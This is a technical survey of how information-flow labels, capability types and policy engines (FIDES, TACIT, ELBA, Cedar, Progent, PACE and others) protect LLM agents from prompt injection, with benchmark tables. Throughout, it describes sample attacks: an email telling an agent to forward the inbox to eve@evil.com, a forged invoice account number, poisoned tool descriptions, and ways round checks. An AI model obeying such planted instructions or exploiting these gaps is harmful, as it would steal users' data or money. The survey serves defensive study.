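Labeling each field separately helps when one result mixes data from several sources. On a bank statement, the bank supplies the dates and amounts, but whoever sends a payment writes its reference text. Separate labels let a plan still use the amounts, whereas a single label would make the entire statement untrusted because of the reference text. Separate labels would not help with Acme's invoice, because an outsider wrote all of it.

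Separate requirements for each argument would help a little more. A payment tool could require a trusted account number but accept an untrusted amount. The agent could then take Acme's account from the address book and the amount from the invoice. An attacker could no longer redirect the money but could still increase the amount, so the tool would also need a spending limit.

For short answers, FIDES can also restrict a quarantined model to $n$ fixed values, so that its answer carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits, or one bit for a yes or no. A policy may treat such an answer as trusted because it has no room for an injected instruction. But a wrong answer can still do damage, however few bits it carries. If the question is whether to pay an invoice, a false "yes" is enough to send the money. This option also doesn't work for account numbers, which have far too many possible values.

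The LLMbda calculus has an explicit `endorse` operation, which marks an untrusted value as trusted. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsing data cannot leak secrets beyond what their theorem already permits. Endorsing does weaken the guarantee about trust, by design. The operation has no effect in code built from untrusted data that has not been endorsed, so an attacker cannot simply inject an endorsement.

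Randori's planner writes any endorsements into its program before it reads real data. On the banking suite, allowing endorsements raised completion from 62.5% to 75% with Alibaba's Qwen3.7-plus and from 54.2% to 64.6% with MiMo-v2.5. The 95% confidence intervals extend about 20 points either way, so the size of the gain is uncertain. Some gain is expected because three of the 16 tasks require the agent to act on a file's contents, which is impossible without endorsement.

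Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs across three models, both with GPT-5.2. In each, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Without endorsement, the label check would have blocked the payment, but it would also have blocked every genuine payment requested this way. Garby and colleagues argue that a user who asks the agent to pay the bill in a file has authorised it to trust that file. That is reasonable only if nobody else can change the file.

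The user can also endorse data while a task is running. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) presents Prudentia, an agent built on top of FIDES. Its planner receives the labels and policies, and must justify any request to read untrusted data. If an email lists ten things to do, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate calls. Prudentia has no equivalent for secrecy, because whether releasing private data is appropriate depends on the particular action.

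Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparisons exaggerate the drawbacks of label checks. In practice, agents without these checks often ask the user to approve each consequential call, but benchmarks ignore the burden of those approvals. They therefore count the calls that would need approval. On AgentDojo, basic label checks reduced that number by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of tasks completed. Prudentia reduced it by a factor of up to 1.9 compared with FIDES, and completed up to 9% more tasks when it could not ask for help. SPA's 29.0% likewise includes only the tasks it completes without asking the user, and asking about refused plans might let it complete some of the rest.

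These counts come from runs without attacks and assume that the user approves every request. They measure how often the agent interrupts the user, not how well people judge the requests. In Anthropic's test, people caught only 13.6% of dangerous commands, and a changed digit in an account number is harder to spot than a dangerous command. A single endorsement also covers everything in the email, including anything an attacker has added. If the user endorses Acme's invoice, Tuesday's payment goes ahead whether or not the account number is genuine. To verify the number, the user would have to compare it with one from a trusted source, and the plan could then use that source instead.

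## Using a programming language's types to limit an agent

SPA keeps its plans easy to check by leaving out functions, so a plan can't include even simple arithmetic. Some programming languages avoid this trade-off by making each function declare, in its type, what it may affect. An agent can then write ordinary programs with loops, arithmetic and functions, and a compiler can reject a dangerous program before it runs.

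### Types, effects and capabilities

A type is a kind of value, such as a whole number or a piece of text. A function's type signature lists the types of its inputs and result. Before a program runs, the compiler checks every use of a function against the function's signature and rejects the program if any use doesn't match. For example, it would reject a program that tries to take the square root of a name.

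An effect is anything a function does besides computing its result, such as reading a file or sending an email. A function with no effects, such as one that adds two numbers, is pure. In most languages, a function's signature does not show its effects, so a function that shortens a text can have the same signature as one that shortens it and also uploads it to a stranger. The designs below use languages that record effects in types.

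One way to limit an agent is with object capabilities. An object capability is an ordinary program value, such as an open file or a network connection, that lets code holding it perform a particular action. Code can use the network only if other code has given it a network capability, which it cannot create itself from, say, the text of a web address. A program can also give a capability to only some of its code. For example, it can download a document in one step and analyse it in another that has no network access.

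### A wrapper for secret text

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, an MCP server from the Swiss university EPFL. An agent submits programs written in Scala 3, and TACIT compiles each one and runs it only if it passes the compiler's checks. Like `run_shell`, TACIT accepts code as an argument, but its compiler can determine which effects the code may have.

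TACIT is meant for an agent that runs on a cloud model and has to work with secret files. Everything the agent reads goes to the model's provider, so Odersky and colleagues treat the model as a possible attacker. When a program reads a file the operator has marked as secret, it receives the text inside a wrapper of type `Classified[String]`. The agent has no function to extract the text. It can call `map`, which applies a function to the hidden text and wraps the result, but `map` accepts only pure functions.

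```scala
val notice = readClassified("secrets/notice.txt")

notice.map(text => text.trim)       // accepted
notice.map(text => println(text))   // rejected
```

The first `map` removes spaces from the ends of the text. This uses no capability, so the compiler gives the function the type `String -> String`, where the plain arrow means that the function is pure. The second would print the text, and anything the program prints goes to the agent's model. Printing requires an input/output capability, so the compiler gives that function a type like `String ->{io} Unit`, which names the capability in braces (`Unit` means that the function returns nothing useful). Since `map` accepts only pure functions, the compiler reports a mismatch. It would reject a function that wrote the text to an ordinary file for the same reason. The check does not depend on the agent's intentions or the file's contents.

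The agent can still work with the text by sending it to a second model that the operator trusts, perhaps one running on the company's computers. That model's answer comes back in the same wrapper. If the agent prints the answer, TACIT shows the user the real text but shows the cloud model only `Classified(****)`. This resembles the quarantined model in SPA, except that the planner can write any pure function to process the hidden text.

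### Expiring file access and banned features

A program gets access to ordinary files by calling `requestFileSystem` with the name of a folder and a block of code. The block receives a file-system capability that expires when the block ends. The agent might try to keep the access by returning a function that reads a file later:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("notes.txt").read()
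}
```

The compiler rejects this program because it cannot give `later` a valid type. The type of the returned function must mention `fs`, the capability the function uses, but `fs` does not exist outside the block. TACIT enforces some file limits at run time rather than through types. It checks that a path is inside the permitted folder only when the program tries to open that path.

These checks work only if a program cannot hide which capabilities it uses. TACIT therefore compiles agents' programs in a "safe mode" that bans several Scala features, including unchecked casts, which make the compiler treat a value as having a different type, and reflection, which lets a program look up functions by name while it is running. Safe mode also restricts programs to library functions whose developers have declared them safe.

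*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same group, illustrates the benefit of checking a whole program before running it. In one example, a program subtracts 50 from an account balance of 100 and then returns text where the caller expects a number. An ordinary Python program would change the balance before reaching the faulty line. The Scala compiler rejects the whole program, so the balance stays at 100. A program that passes the check can still fail halfway, for instance because a service is down.

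### TACIT's tests

To test the wrapper, Odersky and colleagues built a software project with a folder of secrets that included passwords and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 planted instructions, for 120 trials. In 11 other trials, the user was the attacker and either asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone entitled to them, such as an administrator replacing passwords in an emergency. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

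| Model | Secure trials with wrapper | Secure trials without wrapper | Legitimate tasks completed with wrapper | Legitimate tasks completed without wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

The wrapper prevented leaks in two of the 131 trials with Claude and 11 with MiniMax. Planted instructions caused three of these 13 leaks, all with MiniMax. The other ten came from malicious users, to whom MiniMax leaked secrets in 8 of 11 trials. The perfect scores with the wrapper mainly confirm that the software works as designed, since the cloud model never received the secrets as readable text. The comparison is more useful as evidence about the models, because it shows that training alone protected the secrets fairly well in Claude and poorly in MiniMax. Odersky and colleagues say Claude's lower completion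 rate without the wrapper may be an artefact, because Claude often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user.

A test of whether writing typed programs makes agents less capable used τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations. Each model attempted every task ten times with ordinary tool calls and ten times with Scala programs.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, typed programs | Retail, tool calls | Retail, typed programs |
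|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Typed programs scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher. Odersky and colleagues credit clearer return values and the compiler's error messages. But a program can also combine several calls in one step, and the experiment did not test untyped programs, so it cannot separate the effect of types from that of writing code. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults, MiniMax fixed 41.7% with typed programs and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five faults.

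On τ²-bench, the compiler rejected only 0.32% to 7.93% of programs, depending on the model and the domain, and those usually passed after one or two retries. Retrying is also safer here than in CaMeL, where a failed run can reveal something about a secret. A type error depends only on the program's text, so it reveals nothing about the contents of a wrapped value.

LACUNA's results on the same benchmark are less encouraging. In LACUNA, a developer's program contains gaps that a model fills with code when the program reaches them. DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% of 392 tasks this way, compared with 90.0% using ordinary tool calls. That 14-point drop is large, although Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". The compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's programs for retail tasks, and 89% of those that a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote for tasks about telephone service. Zhao and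 colleagues suggest that models have seen much less Scala than Python in training. TACIT and LACUNA differ in too many ways to isolate the cause of their different results, but TACIT's small gains do not carry over to every typed interface.

### TACIT and LACUNA on AgentDojo

Both groups also adapted AgentDojo's tasks and compared their results with CaMeL's published figures for the same models. The table shows the share of tasks completed in each suite and the number of successful attacks in about 950 attacked runs.

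| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |

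TACIT and CaMeL had comparable completion rates in banking, but with o4-mini-high TACIT completed far fewer tasks than CaMeL in workspace and Slack, and with Gemini CaMeL completed almost no tasks in travel. Odersky and colleagues nonetheless describe the two systems' completion rates as comparable. The one attack counted as successful against TACIT was arguably a scoring error. The user asked the agent to book a hotel whose reviews contained an attacker's recommendation for a different hotel. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo counted the mention of the other hotel as a success for the attacker.

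These results give little evidence about whether TACIT can stop an attacker who changes a value. In the banking version, the signature of the function that sends money lists no capability, and according to the agent's instructions, effects inside `map` happen immediately. So an agent could apparently call that function from inside `map` and pay an account number it had never seen. TACIT probably resisted the planted instructions because the agent never read them, as in SPA. If someone had altered the account number on Acme's invoice, the agent could still have sent the money to the wrong account.

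LACUNA's eight failures point to a related weakness. Its compiler limits each program to the capabilities that the developer made available at that point. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker can still succeed by getting the model to misuse one of those capabilities.

### A bibliography that accepts only DBLP records

Types can also restrict where a value comes from. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives the example of an agent that compiles a bibliography. Language models sometimes invent references, so the developer wants every entry to come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications.

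If the agent can run any code, it can write an invented entry straight to the file. The developer could instead offer a narrow tool that fetches a record from DBLP and adds it to the file in a single step. That would keep out invented entries, but an agent asked for the earliest paper on a topic would have to read the records one by one, because it could not write code to sort them by date.

Zhou and colleagues get around this with ELBA, their implementation of language-based agent control in the programming language Haskell. The developer provides three functions, with signatures roughly like these:

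```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

`dblpSearch` takes a search phrase and returns a list of DOIs, which are identifiers for publications. `dblpFetchBib` takes a DOI and returns the publication's record in a wrapper named `Trusted`. Only the developer's library can create or modify that wrapper, and `appendToBibFile` accepts only records wrapped in it. The agent can read and sort records, but it cannot pass text it wrote itself to `appendToBibFile` as a record.

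The agent might still try to use Haskell's general function for writing files instead of `appendToBibFile`. ELBA prevents this by requiring the agent's whole program to have the type `BibIO`, which marks computations whose only effects are those of the developer's three functions.

```haskell
do { entry <- dblpFetchBib doi; appendToBibFile entry }   -- accepted
writeFile "refs.bib" "an invented entry"                  -- rejected
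```

The compiler rejects the second program because `writeFile` has the type `IO ()`, which permits any input or output, but ELBA requires `BibIO ()`. The agent can still use any code without effects, so it can filter, count and sort.

In a test with Claude Sonnet 5 and 100 computer science topics, an ordinary agent with web search got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations. The ELBA agent made no such errors in 925 citations. Part of this difference comes from the tools, because the ordinary agent had no function for fetching DBLP records and wrote the entries itself. The narrow tool described above should also have produced no invented entries. Types add the freedom to compute with the records, but they do not ensure that the agent picks relevant papers or that DBLP is right.

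The same pattern would work for Acme's invoice. A payment function could accept only a value of type `Payee`, which only the address-book function can create. The agent could write any program that calls the payment function, but an account number from an invoice would have the wrong type. As with a list of saved payees, the agent could not pay a new supplier until someone had added the supplier to the address book.

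### How subagents inherit limits

An agent in ELBA writes a complete program each time, so it cannot read a search result and then decide what to do unless the program calls a model again, which creates a subagent. For example, the bibliography agent can search DBLP, fetch the first record and pass it to a subagent that decides whether to refine the search.

The subagent's code becomes part of the surrounding program, so its type has to fit there. Inside a `BibIO` program, a subagent that has effects must also be a `BibIO` program, and it can write to the file only through `appendToBibFile`. If the first agent asked for a subagent of type `IO ()`, the compiler would reject the request just as it rejects `writeFile`. The first agent can impose tighter limits by asking for a plain `Int` (a whole number), which lets the subagent calculate but not have any effects. Even if a hostile message leads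 that subagent to write a command that deletes files, the program will not compile.

File access can be narrowed in a similar way. In another of Zhou and colleagues' examples, functions that read and write files accept only a `Path`, a capability for a particular folder. An agent can turn a project's `Path` into one for a single subfolder and give only that to a subagent, but it cannot make a `Path` from the text `"/etc/passwd"`. As in TACIT, part of the checking happens while the program runs, because a shortcut inside the folder might lead outside it.

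Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents does not weaken the host language's guarantees. Let $e$ be a program, $t$ a type and $\text{traces}(e)$ the set of all sequences of visible tool calls that $e$ can produce. A property $P$ is one that the type system enforces if

$$\vdash e : t \implies P(\text{traces}(e)) \quad \text{for every program } e.$$

This means that every program with type $t$ has property $P$, such as writing only DBLP records. The theorem extends this to programs that contain agent calls. To prove it, Zhou and colleagues replace each call with an ordinary function that gets code from a model, checks the code's type and runs it. The result is a program in the original language with the same type and the same traces, so $P$ still holds. Generated code may contain further agent calls, so they repeat the argument for each level of subagents, up to a fixed maximum depth.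 The theorem assumes that the host language is sound, and it does not establish whether the types express the right rule.

### ELBA's results on AgentDojo

For AgentDojo's Slack tasks, Zhou and colleagues used LIO, an existing Haskell library for information-flow control. Like FIDES, LIO keeps one label for everything read so far, so once an agent has read a page from an unknown website, LIO blocks any action that requires more trust. Here, types only ensure that the agent's program goes through LIO. LIO makes its checks at run time, so a program may send one message before LIO blocks the next.

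A subagent can read the page instead and return its answer as a labelled value that the first agent does not open. The subagent works like a quarantined model, except that it may still call tools that accept data at its level of trust.

The table shows how many of the 21 user tasks ELBA and CaMeL completed without an attack.

| Model | ELBA, with policies | CaMeL, with policies | ELBA, without policies | CaMeL, without policies |
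|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

With policies on, ELBA completed nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL. There are too few tasks to be confident about the size of the gap for any single model, but in the runs with AgentDojo's direct attack, ELBA's lead was statistically clear for all four models. Much of the lead probably comes from ELBA's ability to read one result before deciding what to do next, though the repeated model calls also made it take about three times as long as CaMeL. Both systems completed fewer tasks with policies on. Over the four models, ELBA's total fell from 64 of 84 tasks to 37.

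Every model resisted all of AgentDojo's own attacks with or without policies, so those attacks could not be used to measure what the policies contributed. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated an attack that always deceives the model. Whenever a subagent received a planted instruction, they removed the subagent's real task, leaving only the attacker's text. They ran all 105 security cases seven times on each model (735 runs per model).

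| Model | Attack success, without policies | Attack success, with policies | Tasks completed, without policies | Tasks completed, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 42.2% | 0% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Opus 4.8 | 37.4% | 0% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT 5.4 | 15.5% | 0% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Sonnet 5 | 26.5% | 0% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

This is better evidence than most results on AgentDojo because it does not depend on how well a particular attack is worded. The zeros exclude 29 runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks. In these runs, an agent opened a web address without sending data to it, and Zhou and colleagues reviewed each one and found no violation. They did not run this test on CaMeL, but they expect it would also have stopped the attacks.

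### What has to be trusted, and who writes the types

These designs let an agent write much richer programs than SPA does, but their guarantees depend on more software. SPA needs a validator and an interpreter for six kinds of step, while TACIT needs the Scala compiler, the software that runs compiled programs, its own library and the trusted model. A fault in any of these could expose a secret. Using established software partly offsets this risk. Zhou and colleagues point out that researchers have studied LIO and proved it sound, whereas most agent defences rely on new information-flow code of their own. Capture checking is younger, and although its basic type system has machine-checked proofs, which Odersky helped to write, there is no proof yet for safe mode. TACIT's guarantees also don't cover side channels such as timing.

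TACIT's software is still changing. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* calls tracked capabilities the language's most important new feature, but capture checking is still experimental. The developers wrote in the project's repository, lampepfl's *TACIT*, that they were enforcing safe mode by searching programs for forbidden patterns. A later version of the documentation, Glama's *TACIT*, says the compiler's own safe mode is now on by default alongside that search.

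An operator can also undo the protection by misconfiguring the system. TACIT checks only the programs that reach it, so its developers advise switching off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and web access. If an agent uses TACIT to run another program, such as `git`, the Scala compiler cannot control what that program does. The later version can send a secret, without unwrapping it, to an approved web server, for example to log in. If the operator does not set a list of approved servers, the only limit is the list in the agent's own program. A hijacked agent could then apparently list an attacker's server and send it the secret.

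The documentation also states that the wrapper protects confidentiality but not integrity. The agent can wrap any text and, by default, write it over a secret file, such as the one that determines who may log in to a computer. Operators can prevent this by making secret files read-only.

Someone also has to write the signatures correctly. If a developer forgets to record that a function uses the network, the compiler will treat the function as pure and let it handle secrets. TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and Odersky and colleagues estimate that each new domain takes a few hundred more, mostly translations of existing tool descriptions. They argue that only the reusable library requires expertise in capture checking. But the payment function in their AgentDojo version lists no capability, which shows that the translations matter too. A reviewer has to notice what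 is missing from a signature, which is harder than reading what is there.

Some common rules are also hard to express with ordinary types. A type can require a payment to go to a saved payee, but it cannot easily limit the agent to $500 a day, because the compiler has no record of what the agent has already spent. Odersky and colleagues suggest putting checks of this kind, such as limits on how often an agent may act, in TACIT's library functions, where they would run on every call.

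## Rules that allow or refuse each action

Software can check each tool call, as the agent makes it, against a policy, which is a set of rules kept outside the agent. The software can also keep a record of earlier payments, which it needs to enforce a daily spending limit.

A rule can cover a single call, a sequence of calls or a whole plan. For Michelle's email assistant, the rules might be:

| What the rule covers | Example | When software checks it |
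|---|---|---|
| a single call | `send_email` may only write to company addresses | just before the call |
| a sequence of calls | once the agent has called `fetch_mail`, it may not email outsiders | before each call, using a record of earlier calls |
| a whole plan | no step may pass the text of an email to an outside address | before any step runs |

### Cedar rules in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore

Bedrock AgentCore is a service from Amazon Web Services (AWS) for running agents. Its policy feature became generally available on 3 March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). A gateway between the agent and its tools checks each request against rules written in Cedar, AWS's open-source language for access permissions.

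A Cedar rule permits or forbids an action by a principal (a user or program) on a resource, and it can set conditions on other details of the request. With simplified, invented names, two rules for payments might be:

```
permit (principal, action == Action::"send_money", resource)
when { context.input.amount <= 500 };

forbid (principal, action == Action::"send_money", resource)
unless { ["acme", "northgate"].contains(context.input.payee) };
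```

The gateway refuses any request that no rule permits, and a `forbid` rule overrides every `permit` rule (AWS News Feed, *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, 2026). For example, the gateway allows a $300 payment to Acme but refuses a $600 payment to Acme because no rule permits it. It also refuses a $300 payment to a stranger, because a `forbid` rule applies.

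Both rules check one request at a time. The agent could pay Acme $500 ten times in a day, and every payment would pass unless other software included the day's total in each request.

Since June 2026, a policy can also use the results of Bedrock Guardrails, which are filters that look for harmful content and sensitive information (AWS, *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy*, 2026). The gateway will always compare an amount with 500 correctly, but a rule that relies on a filter can fail because the filter may miss an attack if the attacker rewords it.

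### AgentSpec's triggers and responses

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, present a rule language with more responses than permitting or refusing. In their example, a user asks an agent to send $100 to Bob. Bob is the user's son and often receives money, but the user may also know another Bob, such as a new employee. This rule makes the agent ask first if the recipient is not a family member:

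```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger Transfer
check !is_to_family_member
enforce user_inspection
end
```

The trigger can be an action, a change in the agent's surroundings or the end of a task. If every condition under `check` is true, AgentSpec prompts the user, stops the agent, runs a predefined action or has the model reconsider. Having the model reconsider gives no guarantee, because it leaves the decision to the model that the rule is meant to control. Someone has to write each condition as a Python function, so this rule works only if `is_to_family_member` can distinguish between the two Bobs.

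Wang and colleagues first tested rules they had written by hand. They gave a programming agent 750 risky instructions, 30 for each of 25 kinds of risk. The agent tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them, or 79%. The rules flagged nothing for two kinds of risk, but the agent's programs for those did not contain the fault that the instructions asked for. Without those two, the figure is 91%, in line with the paper's claim of over 90%. Wang and colleagues inspected the flagged programs and judged 58 to be harmless.

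With rules on, an agent controlling a household robot carried out none of the hazardous instructions, whereas without them it carried out as many as 79% in the worst category. The share of safe tasks it completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. An autonomous vehicle obeyed traffic laws in all eight driving scenarios. Checking a rule's conditions took less than 3 milliseconds on average. Because Wang and colleagues developed the rules for the kinds of risk they then tested, these results mostly show that the language can express useful rules. They are weaker evidence of protection against dangers that a rule's author has not thought of.

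### Progent changes the rules during a task

The right permissions depend on the task. An agent needs `send_email` to send Alice an update, but not to summarise unread mail. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) therefore has a language model write a policy for each task and revise it as the agent learns more.

A Progent rule allows or forbids a tool under conditions on its arguments, and can specify what happens after a refusal. In simplified notation, one rule might be:

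```
allow send_slack_msg when { to == "alice" }
fallback return "Not allowed. Try another tool or argument."
```

Progent's conditions can compare values, test whether a value is in a list, match text patterns and combine tests with "and", "or" and "not". As in Cedar, `forbid` rules take precedence, and Progent refuses any call that no rule allows. When it refuses a call, it returns an error message by default so that the agent can continue with the task.

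Suppose a user asks the agent to do the tasks in Alice's email "TODOs for the week". The initial policy allows only a search for that email. In it, Alice asks for a summary of recent mail to be posted on Slack, so the model proposes also allowing the agent to read mail, look up the user's Slack name and post messages. After the agent learns that the Slack name is `alice`, the model restricts messages to that name. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`. The policy does not allow `send_email`, so Progent blocks the call, and the agent goes on to post the summary.

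The model that revises the policy reads tool results, so an injected instruction could persuade it to allow `send_email`. Progent therefore compares the old and new policies. If $A(P)$ is the set of calls that policy $P$ allows, the change from $P$ to $P'$ is a narrowing when

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P).$$

Progent checks a policy change with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions. The solver looks for a call that the new policy would allow and the old one would refuse. If there is none, the change takes effect automatically. If there is one, as when the model adds `send_email`, the change is an expansion and needs approval. Shi and colleagues call this guarantee monotonic confinement, meaning that the set of allowed calls can only shrink without approval.

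Progent applies an update without asking if it narrows the set of allowed actions, even though the smaller set may be wrong. For example, if the agent may message anyone on Slack, Progent would apply an update that allows only messages to `eve`.

With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, Progent lowered the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% while largely maintaining task completion. On Agent Security Bench, another set of simulated attacks, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues left out two of AgentDojo's travel attacks, which steer the agent towards a different hotel, because Progent is not designed to stop an attacker from influencing which permitted option the agent chooses.

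These tests automatically approved every expansion to simulate a careless user. Monotonic confinement therefore did not protect the agent, and the low rates depended on the model rarely writing a rule that the attacker needed. The initial policy without updates reduced the rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Refusing every expansion gave a slightly lower rate than approving them all, but in the example above it would have prevented the agent from doing anything on Alice's list.

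With a human reviewing the initial policy and every expansion of it, no attack succeeded. That result assumes the reviewer always refuses a malicious recipient and never allows unrestricted payments. Anthropic's testers were less reliable than that, even when reviewing single commands. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so reviewers would have fewer decisions to make.

### Rules that remember earlier calls

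An attacker who knows that an agent may send at most $500 at a time can get around this limit by having it send several smaller payments. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested this kind of attack on a system that translates each proposed action into logical constraints and has a solver check them against fixed rules. No attack succeeded in the paper's payment scenario, and the system did not block any legitimate action. The core check took 0.44 milliseconds on average. These results are encouraging but narrow, since the evaluation covered only two scenarios, both built by the researchers. The system's security guarantee also assumes that the agent cannot act without going through the checker.

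Meijer describes rules on sequences of calls as security automata, which are small machines with a list of states and rules for moving between them. An automaton for the mailbox attack could start in the state "no mail read" and move to "mail read" when the agent calls `fetch_mail`. From that state, a call to `send_email` with an outside address leads to an error state. A monitor tracks the state as the agent makes calls and refuses any call that would lead to the error state.

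This automaton would stop the theft of Michelle's mail. It would also stop her assistant from sending an unrelated note to a supplier later in the session, because the automaton records which calls the agent made but not which data they used. As Meijer notes, a monitor also acts late, because the agent has already read private messages by the time the monitor blocks the email.

Some rules require a call instead of forbidding one. Doshi and colleagues propose that their calendar agent must email each attendee immediately after every `update_event`. A monitor that can only refuse calls cannot make the agent send those emails. It can refuse every other call until the agent has sent them, but if the agent stops before sending them, other software has to do it.

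### PACE checks where a call's values came from

A monitor can be more precise if it also records which data reach a call. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that does this just before each tool runs. PACE freezes the call's arguments and looks for matching values among earlier tool results, the user's request and other data. It uses the matches to build a graph of how data may have reached the call. If a path leads from untrusted or secret data to a dangerous effect, PACE proposes a way to cut it, usually by blocking the call.

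A separate check determines whether the user's request authorises the effect. PACE derives permissions, including limits on resources, arguments and spending, from that request alone, so nothing in an email can add permissions.

Li and colleagues tested the two checks separately and together on a subset of several benchmarks, with Qwen-3.8-27B as the agent. The full system also has a component that adapts how the system carries out a decision, for example by repairing a call.

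| | AgentDojo attack success | AgentDojo tasks completed | AgentDyn attack success | AgentDyn tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Data-path check only | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Authority check only | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Full system | 0.0% | 67.2% | 0.0% | 33.3% |

The data-path check stops attacks largely by blocking most tool calls. On the AgentDyn tasks, it proposed a cut for 5,842 of 6,647 calls. The full system completes more tasks because it lets a blocked call through when the authority check approves it. This also restores the suspicious path, so the formal guarantee about data paths no longer holds for that call. Li and colleagues describe a stricter version that keeps the guarantee, but they report no results for it. Even the stricter version does not cover text that the model has paraphrased. FIDES and SPA avoid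 that gap by labelling a model's whole answer according to everything the model read.

Across eight full benchmarks and three models, PACE had or tied for the lowest attack success rate in 76 of 79 comparisons. Its task completion rate was at most three percentage points below that of an undefended agent. On the subset above, however, AgentDyn completion fell by half.

The same experiments also tested Progent on MCPTox, a benchmark in which the attacker controls tool descriptions. With gpt-5.6-luna, Progent lowered the worst attack success rate from 86.9% to 46.4%, but the agent's refusal rate rose from 28.0% to 78.4%. This is much weaker than Progent's result on AgentDojo, probably because its policy writer trusts the tool descriptions it reads. However, the comparison comes from a competing team, which also measured a 36.1% attack success rate for CaMeL on AgentDojo with the same model,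 although CaMeL's published results for other models include at most one successful attack in about 950 runs. Differences in the models, attacks or setup may therefore explain part of Progent's weak result.

### Proving that a plan follows the rules

In Meijer's design, a verifier checks the model's complete plan for violations before the agent does anything, much as a compiler checks a typed program.

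An email cannot change a plan that the model wrote before reading it, but a poisoned tool description can. Suppose the description of `fetch_mail` persuades the model to plan three steps: fetch Michelle's mail, summarise it, and email the summary to an outsider "for compliance". A source-and-sink rule names a source of data and a destination that the data must not reach. In simplified form, Meijer's rule is:

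```json
{"source": {"tool": "fetch_mail", "value": "result"},
 "sink":   {"tool": "send_email", "argument": "body",
            "condition": {"to": {"notIn": ["*.valleysharks.com"]}}}}
```

The verifier starts with the result of `fetch_mail` and follows it through the plan. The summary depends on the emails, and the plan would send it in the body of a message to an address outside the company. The verifier therefore rejects the plan before the agent fetches any mail. It would also reject the plan if Michelle herself had asked for the extra step. Meijer suggests using existing program-analysis tools, such as CodeQL or Semgrep.

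His other case, in which the model meets a request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` by planning `delete_file("*.txt")`, requires a more exact description of what a plan should achieve. To check the plan, the verifier needs a postcondition, a statement that must be true when the plan has finished. If $F$ is the set of files before the plan runs and $F'$ the set afterwards, an obvious postcondition is

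$$\text{foo.txt} \notin F' \quad \text{and} \quad \text{bar.txt} \notin F'.$$

The plan satisfies it, since deleting every text file also deletes these two. What is missing is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. Adding one gives

$$F' = F \setminus \{\text{foo.txt}, \text{bar.txt}\},$$

which means that exactly those two files disappear. The verifier must now reject `*.txt`, because the folder might contain another text file.

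Meijer writes his frame condition into the tool's description, which guarantees that `delete_file` leaves alone any file that does not match its pattern. The verifier needs this guarantee to prove that a plan with two separate deletions is safe. But the guarantee does not rule out a call with the pattern `*.txt`, because every file that call deletes matches the pattern. Ruling out that call requires a separate frame condition for the user's task, as in the formula above.

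Meijer's article proposes a design but reports no measurements, so it does not show how many harmful plans a verifier would catch or how many useful ones it would reject. Meijer acknowledges that nobody has formally measured how writing a plan first affects an agent's answers, though he expects it to help.

### Who writes the rules

In the deletion example, the proof guarantees only what the postcondition states. Small mistakes can also disable a rule. Meijer's article calls the mail tool `fetch_mail` in its plan but `fetch_email` in its rule, so a checker that compared the names literally would find no match and allow the plan.

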